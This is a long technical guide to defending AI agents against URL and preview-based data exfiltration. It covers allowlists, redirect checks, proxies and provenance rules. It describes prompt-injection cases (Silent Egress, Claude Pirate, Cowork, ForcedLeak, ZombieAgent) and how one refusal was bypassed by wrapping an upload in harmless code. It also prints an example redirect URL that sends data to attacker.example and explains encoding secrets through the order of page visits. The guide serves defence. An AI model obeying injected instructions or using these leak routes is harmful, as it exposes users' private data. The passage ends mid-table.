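PromptArmor wants messaging apps to offer preview settings for individual chats, and agent developers to use whatever settings exist. For OpenClaw on Telegram, the setting already existed, but users were exposed because they wouldn't look for the setting unless they knew about the danger.

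### The Silent Egress experiments

An agent can leak data without a messaging service by calling its own fetch tool. *Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026) measured how often this happened with one small model. "Egress" means outgoing network traffic, and the leak is silent because the user sees an ordinary answer.

The researchers, who work at eBay, built a test agent around qwen2.5:7b, an open model with about seven billion parameters, and ran it on their own machines at a temperature of 0.7. The user always asked the agent to summarise a page. The agent's software automatically fetched the page and gave the model its title, description and text, much as a messaging service collects material for a preview. This material contained a hidden instruction to make a web request that included a secret from the model's context. A second server recorded any requests it received.

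They varied three things:

- where the instruction was: the title, the description, the body of the page or the text of a link
- whether the agent reached the page directly or through redirects, in which one address sends the visitor on to another
- whether the model was to send the secret whole or in four pieces.

This gave 16 combinations, each run 30 times. The agent contacted the attacker's server in 423 of the 480 runs (88.1 per cent) and in none of the 120 control runs with harmless pages. Redirects made almost no difference, and neither did the position of the instruction when the model sent the secret whole.

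In 95 per cent of the successful attacks, the final answer to the user looked harmless. A safety check limited to the agent's answers would have missed nearly all of these attacks, though they would have appeared in a log of outgoing requests.

#### Splitting the secret

An attacker who expects a filter to look for complete passwords can ask the model to send a few characters at a time. The agent contacted the server in 238 of 240 runs when told to send the secret whole, but in 185 of 240 when told to split it. Splitting requires several correct tool calls, and the small model often failed.

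Lan and colleagues also report that splitting reduced a measure called Leak@1 by 73 per cent, from 0.967 to 0.263. They define Leak@*k* as the share of runs in which any piece of the secret appears in the first *k* requests. By this definition Leak@3 can't be lower than Leak@1, because the first three requests include the first one. Yet the paper gives a Leak@3 of 0.158 for split secrets, so either the definition or the count must be wrong.

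Even without this error, the 73 per cent would be hard to interpret. A run should count as a leak if the model sends the first piece correctly. The fall may mean that the measure missed short pieces, which would make splitting a good disguise, or that the model often sent the wrong data, which would make splitting a poor attack. The figures for contact with the server are more reliable, but they show only that splitting made the attack fail more often.

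#### Warning the model or blocking the request

The researchers then tested each defence 30 times on the simplest version of the attack, in which the instruction was in the body of the page and the secret was sent whole.

| Defence | Model tried to contact the attacker | Request got out |
|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 100% |
| Warning in the model's instructions | 66.7% | 66.7% |
| Tags marking web text as untrusted | 100% | 100% |
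| Warning and tags | 56.7% | 56.7% |
| Allowlist of domains | 100% | 0% |
| Filter for suspicious addresses | 83.3% | 0% |
| Filter for words such as "password" | 23.3% | 0% |
| Filter for random-looking values | 0% | 0% |
| All of these together | 0% | 0% |

The allowlist worked better than the warning. The warning told the model never to follow instructions from web content, but the model still followed them in 20 of 30 runs. With the allowlist, the model tried to follow them in every run, and the software blocked each attempt. The allowlist works because blocking doesn't depend on the model, although attackers can sometimes route data through a permitted site, as the next section explains.

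The zero results for the three filters are much weaker evidence. The filter for suspicious addresses blocks paths containing words such as "collect". The attack in the paper sends its data to `/collect`, but an attacker could avoid the filter by choosing a path without such words.

The filter for random-looking values uses Shannon entropy, which measures how unpredictable the characters in a string are:

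*H* = −Σ *p*ᵢ log₂ *p*ᵢ

Here *p*ᵢ is the share of the string made up of the *i*-th distinct character. The filter blocks any value longer than ten characters with an *H* above 4.0. The paper's example of a secret, `SECRET_API_KEY_12345`, has an *H* of about 3.85, so it would pass. A four-character piece is too short for the filter to check, and its *H* could never exceed 2.

The table also shows that this filter never blocked anything, because the model made no attempt in any of the 30 runs. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model avoids random-looking values when something is monitoring it. But the filter they describe inspects finished requests, and they mention no way the model could have known about it. An unnoticed difference between the test runs seems a more likely explanation. The same doubt applies to the word filter, because attempts fell to 23.3 per cent with it. None of the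 defence tests used split secrets, so the paper's claim that splitting gets past such filters is based on how they work, not on a measurement.

### How far the result carries over to current systems

The 88 per cent is not a reliable estimate for a current commercial agent. The model tested, Qwen2.5, dates from 2024 and is small, with seven billion parameters. The researchers also acknowledge that they made the attacker's job easy. They put the secret in the model's context, gave the model almost no instructions beyond the format for tool calls, and passed on web pages without removing hidden text.

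Lan and colleagues nevertheless argue that their figures may understate the danger, because their injected instructions were simple and a more capable model follows instructions more closely and handles tools and multi-step tasks better. The last point is plausible for split secrets, where the small model's mistakes protected the user. But developers also train newer models to resist injected instructions, as OpenAI does for its browser agent. An experiment with one model can't show which effect is larger.

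The attack route does carry over, because any agent that holds private data, reads text from strangers and can cause a web request has everything the attack needs. Rehberger's 2025 demonstrations on commercial Claude products and a May 2026 case on a Microsoft product, described below, show that the attack can work on larger systems, but they don't establish how often it succeeds.

People also appear to be planting such instructions. Infosecurity Magazine's *Researchers Uncover 10 In-the-Wild Prompt Injection Payloads Targeting AI Agents* reports on ten examples that the security company Forcepoint found on real web pages. One is a request for a secret API key, but it may be part of a puzzle, because it also mentions a "flag", the usual name for the hidden prize in a hacking contest.

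A builder can get a more relevant figure by repeating the experiment with the product's own model, instructions and tools, a fake secret and a private server. The builder should use the server's log to judge whether a run counts as a leak, since the agent's answer will usually look normal. The builder also needs runs with harmless pages to measure how often the agent contacts the server for no reason.

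### Turning previews off

On Slack, software that posts a message can turn off the message's link previews by setting `unfurl_links: false`, which covers pages of text, and `unfurl_media: false`, which covers images, video and audio. Both are necessary because an attacker can use an address that leads to an image. Slack confirms that the two settings together stop its servers from fetching the link.

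Setting both explicitly is better than relying on the defaults. According to Slack's documentation, Slack previews all links in messages from apps, but one of the documentation's examples is a link to a text page that gets no preview unless the app asks for one. Slack also shows no preview when a link's label is the same as its address without the scheme. This exception applies when an agent's software turns a filename into a link with the label `README.md` and the address `http://README.md`. The documentation is unclear on whether Slack's servers still fetch the address in that case.

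The code that posts the message should set the two fields. If the model can set them when it calls a tool, an injected instruction could lead it to turn previews back on. A reader's own preview setting is not a substitute, because it only changes what that person sees. Slack's servers make the request, and other people in the channel may have different settings.

Turning off previews removes only the title and picture under each link. A builder who wants to keep some previews can allow them only for the company's own sites, as Embrace The Red suggests. In either case, a person can still click the link, which sends the same query to the same host. According to Slack, setting `parse` to `none` leaves addresses as plain text, but Slack still applies its own formatting codes, so a builder should check whether links written in that notation remain clickable. Without links, readers have to copy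 every useful address by hand.

### Proxies, queries and images

A proxy is a server that makes requests on someone else's behalf. If a preview loads through one, the host receives the proxy's network address instead of the reader's. This protects the reader's location but not the data in the query, because the proxy normally requests the full URL. In Rehberger's tests with an image link, the secret reached his server several times, including through Slack's image proxy.

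A proxy prevents the leak only if it blocks or changes some requests. It could fetch only addresses that were already public. PYMNTS's *OpenAI Warns Malicious Links Could Undermine Agentic AI* (2026) reports that OpenAI applies this rule to its agents, and a later section examines it. The drawbacks are that someone has to run the proxy server and that new or private pages would have no previews.

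Another option is to remove the query before fetching. The preview for `https://notes.example/page?word=bicycle` would then come from `https://notes.example/page`. This breaks any page that needs its query, such as search results, and the preview may show the wrong title. An attacker can also still have the model write data into the path or into a subdomain of the attacker's domain. With a subdomain, the DNS lookup reveals the data even if no web request follows. Lan and colleagues did not test leaks through DNS. Removing queries stops careless attacks but should not be the only defence.

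Remote images need a separate fix because they load when someone opens a message, whether or not it has a link preview. The message contains only the image's address, so the reader's program fetches the image from another server. PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* describes an attack on a Microsoft agent that works with a user's documents. A user uploaded a skill file containing hidden instructions, then asked the agent to review the week's work. The agent sent the user a Teams message with images from an attacker's site, and each image's address contained a download link for one of the user's files.

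These links were pre-authenticated, so anyone who had one could download the file without logging in. A limit on address length would not have protected the documents, since a short link gave access to a whole file. Willison (2026) adds that the agent could send emails to the user's own inbox without approval. This can leak data in the same way as posting to a private channel, and seems harmless for the same reason.

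The simplest fix is not to display remote images in anything an agent writes. Users lose web images, which matters more in a shopping assistant than in a coding tool. The agent's software can still attach charts and other images it makes itself, because showing them doesn't require contacting an outside server. Downloading remote images through the developer's server first would hide the reader's network address, but the request would still leak any data in the image's URL.

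A builder can check these fixes with the test domain and server log from the earlier filename test. The agent sends three things through every channel the product supports: a link to a text page, a link to an image and an embedded remote image. Each URL has a different harmless word in its query. Someone then opens each message without clicking anything. If a word appears in the server's log, that route can still leak data, even if the screen shows no preview.

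## Checking the destination: reputation, allowlists and redirects

An agent that browses the web has to fetch some addresses, so its software needs a way to judge a host before contacting it. A reputation check judges the host by what is known about its domain. An allowlist accepts only hosts that someone approved in advance.

### What a reputation check knows

A reputation check looks up a domain in records that security companies collect. These usually include:

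- the domain's age, from the registry's date of registration
- its category, such as bank, adult site or parked domain
- reports of abuse, such as spam, phishing or malware.

Abuse records take time to build up. As Unit 42 explains, a blocklist relies on earlier reports, a threat feed lists a domain only after somebody has seen it in an active attack, and a reputation score requires the domain to have been online long enough to produce data. A domain registered this morning has no such record, so it looks the same as a harmless new one. Unit 42 saw domains go from registration to hostile content within hours, and the criminal behind the Montana Empire kit had prepared the server before buying the domain.

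Criminals can also keep a domain's record clean for longer by showing a harmless page to automated scanners and the hostile one to everyone else. They can target agents the same way. Willison's *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”* describes a 2026 attack on Claude's fetch tool in which only visitors that identified themselves as Claude received the hostile page, so a security company's scanner would have detected nothing wrong.

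The registration date is harder to hide, so a check can treat a recent one as a warning in itself. This doesn't help with pages on shared hosting. The fake Wells Fargo login page on Google Sites, for example, was on an old, well-regarded Google domain.

Claude Code has a check of this general kind. According to Anthropic, its WebFetch tool contacts `api.anthropic.com` for a "domain safety check", even when a company uses Claude through Amazon, Google or Microsoft, unless the company turns the check off with `skipWebFetchPreflight`. A similar check should send the reputation service only the host, because a full URL might contain private data.

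### Allow or hold

A builder has to decide what happens when a domain has no reputation record. The system can allow the fetch or hold it until a person approves it, the domain has been online longer, or the agent finds another source.

This example uses invented rates to illustrate the drawbacks of each policy. Suppose an agent makes 1,000 fetches, of which 10 go to hostile domains and 990 to harmless ones. The reputation service has a record for 900 of the harmless fetches but only 4 of the hostile ones, since attackers prefer new domains. Among domains with a record, it detects 75 per cent of the hostile ones and wrongly flags 1 per cent of the harmless ones.

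| Result | Allow unknown domains | Hold unknown domains |
|---|---|---|
| Hostile fetches stopped | 3 | 9 |
| Hostile fetches that go ahead | 7 | 1 |
| Harmless fetches stopped | 9 | 99 |
| Hostile share of all stopped fetches | 25% | 8.3% |

Holding unknown domains stops six more hostile fetches and 90 more harmless ones, or 15 harmless fetches for each additional hostile one. It is the better policy if one hostile fetch would do more damage than 15 unnecessary delays. That is likely for an agent that can read a company's mail, and less likely for one that only summarises public pages.

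The last row of the table follows from a general formula. If *h* is the share of all fetches that are hostile, *d* the share of hostile fetches that the policy stops, and *f* the share of harmless fetches that it stops, then:

hostile share of stopped fetches = *hd* / (*hd* + (1 − *h*)*f*)

With the hold policy, *h* is 0.01, *d* is 0.9 and *f* is 0.1, so 8.3 per cent of stopped fetches are hostile. If only one fetch in 1,000 were hostile, that share would fall to 0.9 per cent, and a person reviewing the stopped fetches would find one hostile address in about 110. Hostile fetches are probably rare in ordinary use, so even an accurate check can produce mostly false alarms.

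A builder can replace some of the invented numbers by logging a few weeks of fetches and counting how many went to domains without a record. The share that were hostile is harder to measure, because some attacks go unnoticed.

When OpenAI's own staff use Codex, the company's coding agent, a network policy allows expected destinations, blocks some others, such as the text-sharing site `pastebin.com`, and requires approval for unfamiliar domains (OpenAI, 2026).

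### How to check an address against an allowlist

An allowlist doesn't have to recognise a hostile domain, because it refuses every host that isn't on it. It also works if the model has already accepted an injected instruction, as the Silent Egress experiments showed. But the software has to compare the right part of the address, and do so every time it sends a request:

1. Parse the address and extract the host. In `https://box.com@file.zip`, this is `file.zip`.
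2. Convert the host to lower case and compare all of it with the list.
3. Look up the host's numerical address, and refuse the request if that address belongs to a private network. Otherwise a public name could lead the agent to a machine inside the company.
4. Send the request, with automatic redirects turned off.
5. If the server answers with a redirect, return to step 1 with the new address. Stop after a small number of redirects.

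Products interpret allowlist entries differently. OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* explains that in Codex's local network rules, `example.com` matches only that host, `*.example.com` matches only its subdomains, and `**.example.com` matches both. If one rule allows a host and another denies it, Codex denies it. GitHub says that in its Copilot agent's firewall, a plain entry such as `example.com` also allows every subdomain. Someone who copies an allowlist from Codex to Copilot could therefore allow more hosts than they meant to.

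Step 3 has a gap because an attacker who controls a domain's DNS can return a public address when the software checks it and a private one a moment later, when the software connects. This is called DNS rebinding. Codex blocks hosts that resolve to private addresses, even if they are on the allowlist, and blocks any host whose lookup fails. OpenAI says this reduces the risk but doesn't remove it. To remove it, the software would have to connect to the IP address it checked.

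### Claude Code compared only the start of the name

An error in step 2 affected Claude Code. Its WebFetch tool could contact certain trusted domains, such as `docs.python.org` and `modelcontextprotocol.io`, without asking the user. It recognised them with `startsWith()`, a function that tests only whether one string begins with another. NVD's *CVE-2026-24052 Detail*, the entry in the US government's database of software flaws, gives `modelcontextprotocol.io.example.com` as an example of a name that would have passed.

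That name is a subdomain of `example.com`, so whoever owns `example.com` controls it. Comparing the end of the name is therefore closer to correct, but it also fails if the software ignores the dot between labels. The table shows how three rules treat four hosts when the list contains `modelcontextprotocol.io`.

| Host | Starts with the entry | Ends with the entry | Equals the entry, or ends with a dot and the entry |
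|---|---|---|---|
| `modelcontextprotocol.io` | allow | allow | allow |
| `docs.modelcontextprotocol.io` | refuse | allow | allow |
| `modelcontextprotocol.io.example.com` | allow | refuse | refuse |
| `notmodelcontextprotocol.io` | refuse | allow | refuse |

Only the last rule rejects both names that a stranger could control. If subdomains aren't needed, requiring an exact match is safer still.

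The flaw could have let an attacker receive automatic requests, possibly containing private data, without the user's consent. Anthropic fixed it in version 1.0.111. Users with automatic updates already had the fix when the advisory was published on 3 February 2026, according to GCVE's *GHSA-VHW5-3G5M-8GGF* (2026). The advisory doesn't report an actual attack.

### Redirects from a trusted site

A correct comparison of the first host isn't enough if that host forwards the request. OpenAI gives this as one reason why lists of trusted sites don't fully prevent leaks, since many legitimate websites support redirects. Suppose `trusted.example` is on the list and forwards visitors to any address in its query:

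`https://trusted.example/go?to=https://attacker.example/collect?data=bicycle`

The check finds `trusted.example` and allows the request, but the server replies with a redirect to `attacker.example`. Many programs that make web requests follow redirects automatically, so the second request goes out with "bicycle" in it before the agent's software receives any result. Checking the final address afterwards is too late to stop that request.

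With automatic redirects turned off, the software can check the new host before contacting it and refuse the redirect if necessary. `trusted.example` still receives the word "bicycle", since it was part of the first address, but the attacker doesn't if the redirect is refused.

The same check can interrupt harmless fetches. A download page may forward the agent to a separate host that stores the file, so both hosts have to be on the list. Allowing redirects from trusted sites without checking them would restore the leak, even though it would avoid these interruptions.

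### Claude Cowork's list allowed uploads to an attacker's account

Data can leak even when the software contacts the correct host. This happened with Claude Cowork, Anthropic's desktop agent for office work. Cowork runs code in a virtual machine, a simulated computer separate from the user's own, and its network rules allow connections only to certain hosts. These included `api.anthropic.com`, which Cowork needs to reach Claude.

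Johann Rehberger had found the weakness in an earlier product, the tool that runs code in Claude's ordinary chat. The tool's default network setting was called "Package managers only", but its list also included `api.anthropic.com`. In October 2025, Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate* described the attack:

1. The user asks Claude to analyse a document that contains hidden instructions.
2. Claude follows them and saves private text, such as the user's last conversation, to a file.
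3. Claude runs code that uploads the file to Anthropic's file storage, using an API key that the attacker put in the instructions.
4. The key belongs to the attacker, so the file appears in the attacker's account.

One upload could contain up to 30 megabytes, far more than fits in an address. Claude often refused when it saw the key in the instructions, until Rehberger surrounded the upload with harmless code. He reported the flaw on 25 October 2025, and Anthropic closed the report within an hour as out of scope. Five days later the company confirmed that such reports were in scope and blamed a process error.

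In January 2026, two days after Cowork's release, PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* showed that the same route worked there. A Word document disguised as a skill file contained instructions hidden in tiny white text, and Cowork uploaded a loan estimate from the user's folder without asking for approval. The demonstration used Claude Haiku, a small model, but a second test with Claude Opus 4.5 also leaked customer records.

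Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* describes the fix, a proxy inside the virtual machine that now intercepts requests to `api.anthropic.com`. It passes only those that carry the machine's own session token, so it rejects an attacker's key. It also blocks headers that would make Anthropic's servers fetch something on the agent's behalf. The proxy has to be inside the machine because Anthropic's servers can't tell Cowork's requests apart from other customers' requests. Rehberger had suggested a similar fix, a sandbox that can contact only the logged-in user's account.

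Anthropic now regards each entry on the list as a "capability grant", meaning it permits everything the host can do. Other products' lists have had the same problem. Willison reports that the default list for the browser in Antigravity, Google's coding program, included `webhook.site`, where anyone can create an address and read the requests sent to it. The email program Superhuman allowed images from `docs.google.com`, which also hosts Google Forms, and an attacker used an image address to submit the contents of a user's emails to a form. Docker, whose software runs agents in isolated environments, warns that allowing `github.com` gives an agent access to everything GitHub users publish there, which the agent could use to send data out.

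Limiting the type of request removes some of these capabilities. According to OpenAI's *Agent internet access*, users of Codex's cloud version can restrict it to GET, HEAD and OPTIONS, the HTTP methods for retrieving pages and information about them. This would block a file upload like the one in Cowork, which uses POST, but it would not have protected Superhuman's users, because Google Forms also accepted data from a GET request. Before adding a host to an allowlist, a builder should therefore find out whether a stranger can have an account there and read what others send to it.

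### ForcedLeak used an allowed domain that had expired

A list also goes out of date when a domain changes hands. Researchers at Noma Security demonstrated this in 2025 against Agentforce, the AI agents in Salesforce's customer management software. Çelebi (2025), in *Salesforce Agentforce hit by Noma “ForcedLeak” exploit*, gives the exploit's severity as 9.4 out of 10.

The attack began with a web form that potential customers use to contact a company. Security Affairs' *ForcedLeak flaw in Salesforce Agentforce exposes CRM data via Prompt Injection* notes that the form's description field accepts 42,000 characters, which left plenty of room for hidden instructions. When an employee later asked the agent about the enquiry, the instructions told it to list other customers' email addresses and add an image whose URL contained those addresses.

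Salesforce defended against such images with a Content Security Policy, a list of hosts from which the browser may load material for its pages. The list included every subdomain of `my-salesforce-cms.com`, but that domain had expired and was for sale. The researchers bought it, and their server logged the customers' addresses. According to Salesforce Ben, Noma said the leak would have been impossible without a way around this policy.

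Salesforce recovered the domain and corrected its list. It also began enforcing a list of trusted addresses for its agents, which, according to The Hacker News (2025), stops them from sending output to any other address. This new list applies to the links an agent generates, while the browser's list had controlled only what a page could load. GitHub's *Network Permissions* describes a similar rule for its agent workflows, which replace any address outside the allowed domains with "(redacted)".

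An allowlist entry contains a domain's name but not its owner, so recovering one expired domain doesn't protect the rest of the list. A builder can record the owner, the expiry date and the reason for allowing each domain, and have a script check the registry's records every week. If a domain's registration date is later than the date of its entry, someone has registered the name again, and the software should suspend the entry until a person has reviewed it. This check misses domains that were sold without expiring, because a sale usually doesn't change the registration date. A company should remove its own domains from every allowlist before letting their registrations lapse.

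### Enforcing the list at the network

A check inside the fetch tool applies only to requests made through that tool. Many agents can also run commands, so an agent whose fetch tool has refused `attacker.example` may still be able to reach it with `curl`.

In February 2026, during an internal security exercise at Anthropic, a researcher persuaded an employee to paste a prompt into Claude Code. Among ordinary setup steps, the prompt included instructions to read the employee's Amazon cloud credentials and send them to an outside server. Claude sent the credentials in 24 of 25 repeats. Because the instructions came from the user, the model had little basis for rejecting them. Anthropic concluded that only limits on the agent's environment would have helped, such as blocking the outgoing request or access to the credentials file.

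Claude Code's sandbox limits network access to an allowlist of hosts. The operating system blocks sandboxed commands from reaching the internet except through a proxy outside the sandbox, and the proxy checks each requested host against the list. According to Anthropic, this limit also applies to every program that a command starts, including package installers.

Anthropic says its proxy allows or blocks requests by hostname and doesn't inspect encrypted traffic, so it can't read the path, the query or the data in an upload. Docker's proxy doesn't inspect content either, and Docker also mentions the limitation of domain fronting, in which a program connects using the name of an allowed host but requests a different one inside the encrypted traffic. This works if both hosts use the same delivery network and the network permits it. A proxy that decrypts traffic can catch domain fronting, but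 it also handles the passwords of everyone who uses it, which makes it a target for attackers.

Network rules don't cover a tool that runs outside the environment where they apply. In *Top 6 Claude Cowork Security Risks to Watch*, Borah (2026) says Cowork's web search and web fetch tools bypass its network controls entirely. He works for a company that sells security for agents, but the claim is easy to test. A builder can set up a test domain that isn't on the allowlist and ask the agent to reach it in every way it can, including the fetch tool, the browser, a shell command and a short script. The server's log, or a DNS log for the test domain, will show which attempts got out.

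### What two coding agents allow by default

Codex and Claude Code both restrict the network by default, but their cloud versions have different starting points.

| Agent | Default network access | Requests to other hosts |
|---|---|---|
| Codex on the user's machine | None for commands | Codex asks for approval |
| Codex in the cloud | Full access during setup, then none | Blocked unless the user enables access |
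| Claude Code's sandbox on the user's machine | None | Claude Code asks about each new domain, or an administrator can block them all |
| Claude Code in the cloud | Package registries and other listed domains | Blocked |

The last row comes from Anthropic, which calls this level of access "Trusted". In the cloud version of Codex, setup scripts use the network to install what the project needs, and OpenAI removes any stored secrets before the agent starts. The agent then runs without a network connection, so an attacker who injects an instruction later can't use the network or those secrets.

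"None" applies to the commands that an agent runs, and Codex can still search the web. By default, its search results come from an index that OpenAI maintains, so it doesn't contact the live sites, but OpenAI advises users to treat these results as untrusted. If a user gives Codex full access to the machine, searches go to the live web by default.

### When a short list is enough

OpenAI argues against strict allowlists for agents that browse on a user's behalf. People visit far more than a few well-known sites, so a strict list would produce frequent warnings about harmless pages, and users might learn to click through them. Anthropic describes a similar drawback for literature research with Claude. Free copies of scientific articles are on many hosts, so some downloads fail on a network that allows only listed hosts.

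A coding agent's needs are easier to predict than a browsing agent's. OpenAI's optional "Common dependencies" list for Codex has 71 domains, mostly package registries, code hosts and the sites of programming languages. An agent fixing a bug can often work with fewer, and if its software blocks all other domains without asking, the user sees no warnings. OpenAI is therefore consistent in objecting to allowlists for browsing while offering one for Codex.

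Even this list is broad by the standard of the Cowork case, because it includes `github.com` and `google.com`. If the `google.com` entry also covers subdomains, it allows `docs.google.com`, the host in the Superhuman leak. A team that needs only Python packages could start with an empty list and add `pypi.org` and `pythonhosted.org`.

A builder can test whether a task is narrow enough for an allowlist by running it for a week with the list in logging mode, on a machine without secrets, to see which hosts it needs. If new hosts stop appearing after a few days, the list is ready to enforce. If they keep appearing, the agent is browsing more generally, and its software needs a rule for handling addresses that aren't on the list.

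## Checking where an address came from

Under a provenance check, whether an agent fetches an address depends on where the address came from. This suits agents that browse too widely for an allowlist, because nobody has to judge each host in advance. OpenAI's agents automatically fetch an address if a public web index already contains it. Anthropic's web fetch tool accepts an address if the user or an earlier tool result supplied it. Both companies designed their rules mainly to prevent URL exfiltration.

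### OpenAI's public index

OpenAI announced its rule on 28 January 2026. It relies on a crawler, a program that finds and records public pages as a search engine does. The crawler has no access to users' conversations, accounts or personal data. Before an agent retrieves an address on its own, the software looks for that exact address in the crawler's index. If it is there, the agent loads the page or image. If not, the software either has the agent try a different website or shows the user a warning, which the next section covers.

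OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) calls this mechanism Safe Url. It covers page visits and bookmarks in the Atlas browser, and searches and page visits in Deep Research, ChatGPT's tool for longer investigations. OpenAI says most attacks it knows of fail because the model refuses to take part. Safe Url is for cases where an attacker persuades the model.

OpenAI describes Safe Url as detecting when information from a conversation would go to a third party, but looking up an address in an index doesn't detect secrets. If an address containing a password and the address of an article published ten minutes ago are both missing from the index, the software holds both. This causes false alarms, but it also means an attacker gains nothing by encoding the password or splitting it into pieces, which can defeat a filter that searches for secrets.

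### Why an old address can't contain a new secret

The argument for the rule has four steps:

1. The crawler recorded the address without seeing the conversation.
2. The characters in the address therefore don't depend on anything in the conversation.
3. The agent requests exactly those characters.
4. The server therefore receives an address that would have been the same whatever the user had told the agent.

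The first step fails if the index also collects addresses from users' chats or browsing. Even an index that doesn't can contain a private link if somebody posts it publicly by mistake. OpenAI therefore claims only that a public address is "much less likely" to contain the user's private data.

The third step requires an exact comparison. If the software compared only hosts, `https://notes.example/page?word=bicycle` would pass once the crawler had seen any page on `notes.example`. If the software ignored tracking parameters such as `utm_source` during the comparison but left them in the address it fetched, an attacker could put the secret in those parameters. A builder can avoid this by fetching the address stored in the index instead of the one the model wrote.

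Exact matching also helps with the redirect problem from the previous section. A crawler is unlikely to have recorded the `trusted.example` address ending in "bicycle", so the public-index rule would hold it before the first request.

The fourth step covers the text of the address but not the agent's decision to request it. If an agent visits a certain page only when the user has mentioned an illness, the visit reveals the illness. The argument also doesn't depend on who owns the page, so the rule doesn't protect against harmful instructions on it.

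### Anthropic's rule for its web fetch tool

Anthropic's rule uses the conversation itself as the record of acceptable addresses. Anthropic's *Web fetch 工具*, the Chinese edition of the current documentation for developers, lists three sources from which Claude may take an address:

- messages from the user
- results from client tools, which run in the developer's own software
- results from earlier web searches and web fetches.

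Claude can't fetch an address that appears only in its own output or only in the system prompt, the developer's standing instructions to the model. Results from other tools on Anthropic's servers, such as code execution, don't count as a source either. If an address has no permitted source, the fetch tool returns the error `url_not_in_prior_context`.

If the model puts private text into an address, the result is a new string that normally appears in none of the permitted sources, so the tool refuses it. This holds even if the model is following an injected instruction.

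Willison (2025) liked the idea of a tool that would accept only addresses from a user's prompt, but found that Anthropic's rule was looser. He explains in *30 posts tagged “lethal-trifecta”* that a "user message" is a field in the request to the model, and many applications paste untrusted text into it. If a developer's program puts an incoming email there, the tool treats every address in the email as supplied by the user. Willison still thinks the most protective part of the rule is its ban on addresses that Claude makes up.

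Client tools can weaken that ban. Anthropic notes that a tool may repeat text Claude wrote, for example by printing the command it received or quoting it in an error message. By default, an address in that text counts as a tool result, so Claude may then fetch an address it constructed itself.

Developers can prevent this with the `url_sources` setting, which can turn off any of the three sources or limit which tools' results are accepted. An "except" list excludes the named tools but accepts results from any tool the developer adds later. An "only" list excludes new tools until someone adds them to the list, so it is safer for a product that keeps gaining tools.

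The current tool also refuses addresses that appear to contain a credential, such as a password or an API key, unless the credential is in the system prompt or the text of a user message. This helps if an agent has found a password in a file, but it wouldn't catch other private information, such as a person's name or diagnosis. Addresses can't exceed 250 characters, which limits how much data one request can carry. Anthropic's *Web fetch tool*, an earlier English edition of the documentation, warned of "residual risk" and advised developers to use the tool only in trusted environments or with non-sensitive data.

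The two rules differ most on new pages. OpenAI's rule allows an address only if its crawler found it independently of the conversation, while Anthropic's default rule allows even an address that a website has just generated in response to the agent's previous request.

### Leaking data through a choice of addresses

OpenAI explains its rule more fully in a paper, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*. Johann Rehberger reviewed the paper in Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*. He called the rule a significant improvement but objected that an agent can still reveal information by choosing among public addresses.

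Suppose an attacker's website has 36 indexed pages, and an injected instruction assigns one to each letter and digit. The agent can spell out a secret by visiting the matching pages in order. None of the addresses contains the secret, but the attacker can read it from the order of visits in the server's log. Rehberger described this trick in 2023, and he reports that OpenAI also acknowledges it in its paper.

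The amount that can leak depends on the number of addresses, *N*, and the number of visits, *k*:

information in *k* visits = *k* log₂ *N* bits

A six-digit code has a million possible values, or about 19.9 bits. With 36 pages to choose from, each visit carries about 5.2 bits, so an efficient encoding needs four visits. With 1,000 pages it needs two. A 200-character message would take 200 visits at one character per visit, whereas an address that the model could write freely might carry the whole message in one request. The rule therefore protects long documents much better than short codes. It protects the answer to a yes-or-no question least, because the agent can reveal it by visiting or not visiting a single page.

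OpenAI's rule developed partly in response to attacks that leaked data through the agent's choice of address. According to the news report *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, OpenAI had already restricted the addresses ChatGPT could open after an attack called ShadowLeak. A later attack, ZombieAgent, described by the security company Radware, supplied a ready-made address for each letter and digit. The agent could then leak data one character at a time by opening these addresses, without constructing any itself. OpenAI then stopped ChatGPT from opening a link in an email unless the link was in a well-known public index or the user had supplied it in the chat.

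An attacker therefore has to get the addresses indexed before the attack. Rehberger doubts that this is much of an obstacle for anyone with a large website or blog, which probably has 36 indexed pages already. An attacker could also use thousands of pages and assign a word to each.

Rehberger proposes that agents cache each page for a few minutes, or refuse to visit the same full address twice in a session. If an agent tried to send a server the word "bicycle" by visiting one page per letter, the server would receive "bicyle", because the second visit to the page for "c" would never reach it. The missing letter is easy to guess in this word, but would not be in a random password. These limits make the attack harder but don't prevent it, because an attacker with enough pages could avoid repeated visits. Rehberger had not checked whether OpenAI already applied them.

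Anthropic's tool can return cached pages by default. The cache is meant to improve performance and reduce repeated requests, but it could also hide some repeat visits from an attacker. Developers can cap the number of fetches with `max_uses`, which has no default. A low cap helps against bulk theft, but five visits, each to one of 1,000 pages, could still leak about 50 bits, enough for a random eight-character password of lower-case letters and digits.

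OpenAI also offers a stricter setting, Lockdown Mode, for people at greater risk. Willison reports that it became available to eligible personal accounts in June 2026 and limits outgoing requests that could carry sensitive data. He infers that ChatGPT's normal settings don't provide robust protection against a determined attacker. OpenAI's security chief, Dane Stuckey, replied that the mode isn't meant for everyone, because users lose some functions. Willison's inference is reasonable, since OpenAI acknowledges the leak through public addresses.

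### Links inside fetched pages

The researcher Ayush Paul found a similar weakness in Claude's ordinary chat. Willison (2026) explains that the chat's fetch tool could open addresses from the user and search results, and also links in pages it had already fetched. Paul built a website that got Claude to follow a series of links. Claude's choice of links revealed a user's name, home city and employer, which Claude could access through its memory of past conversations.

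Claude hadn't constructed any of the addresses, so the ban on made-up addresses didn't apply. Unlike the attacker in Rehberger's example, Paul didn't need pages that a crawler had already indexed. A website can create new links during the agent's visit, so blocking repeat visits to the same address wouldn't reliably stop this version either.

Anthropic told Paul that it had already identified the problem internally, and paid him no reward. It then removed the tool's ability to open links found in pages it had fetched. Hackaday's *This Week In Security* also reports this change and says it stopped the attack "for now". Following links from page to page is a normal way to do research, but Claude now has to find the next page through a search or get its address from the user.

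The developer documentation still lists earlier web fetch results as a permitted source by default. A developer whose agent handles private data should therefore exclude `web_fetch` from the `server_tool_results` part of `url_sources`. To test this simply, the developer can let the agent fetch a page with one link to the developer's own server, ask it to open that link, and check the server's log.

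### Four addresses under both rules

The following comparison applies the published rules to four made-up cases. The results are inferred from those rules, not taken from an experiment. The comparison assumes that OpenAI's software also accepts addresses supplied by the user, and that Anthropic's tool uses its default settings.

| Address | OpenAI's rule | Anthropic's rule | Possible harm |
|---|---|---|---|
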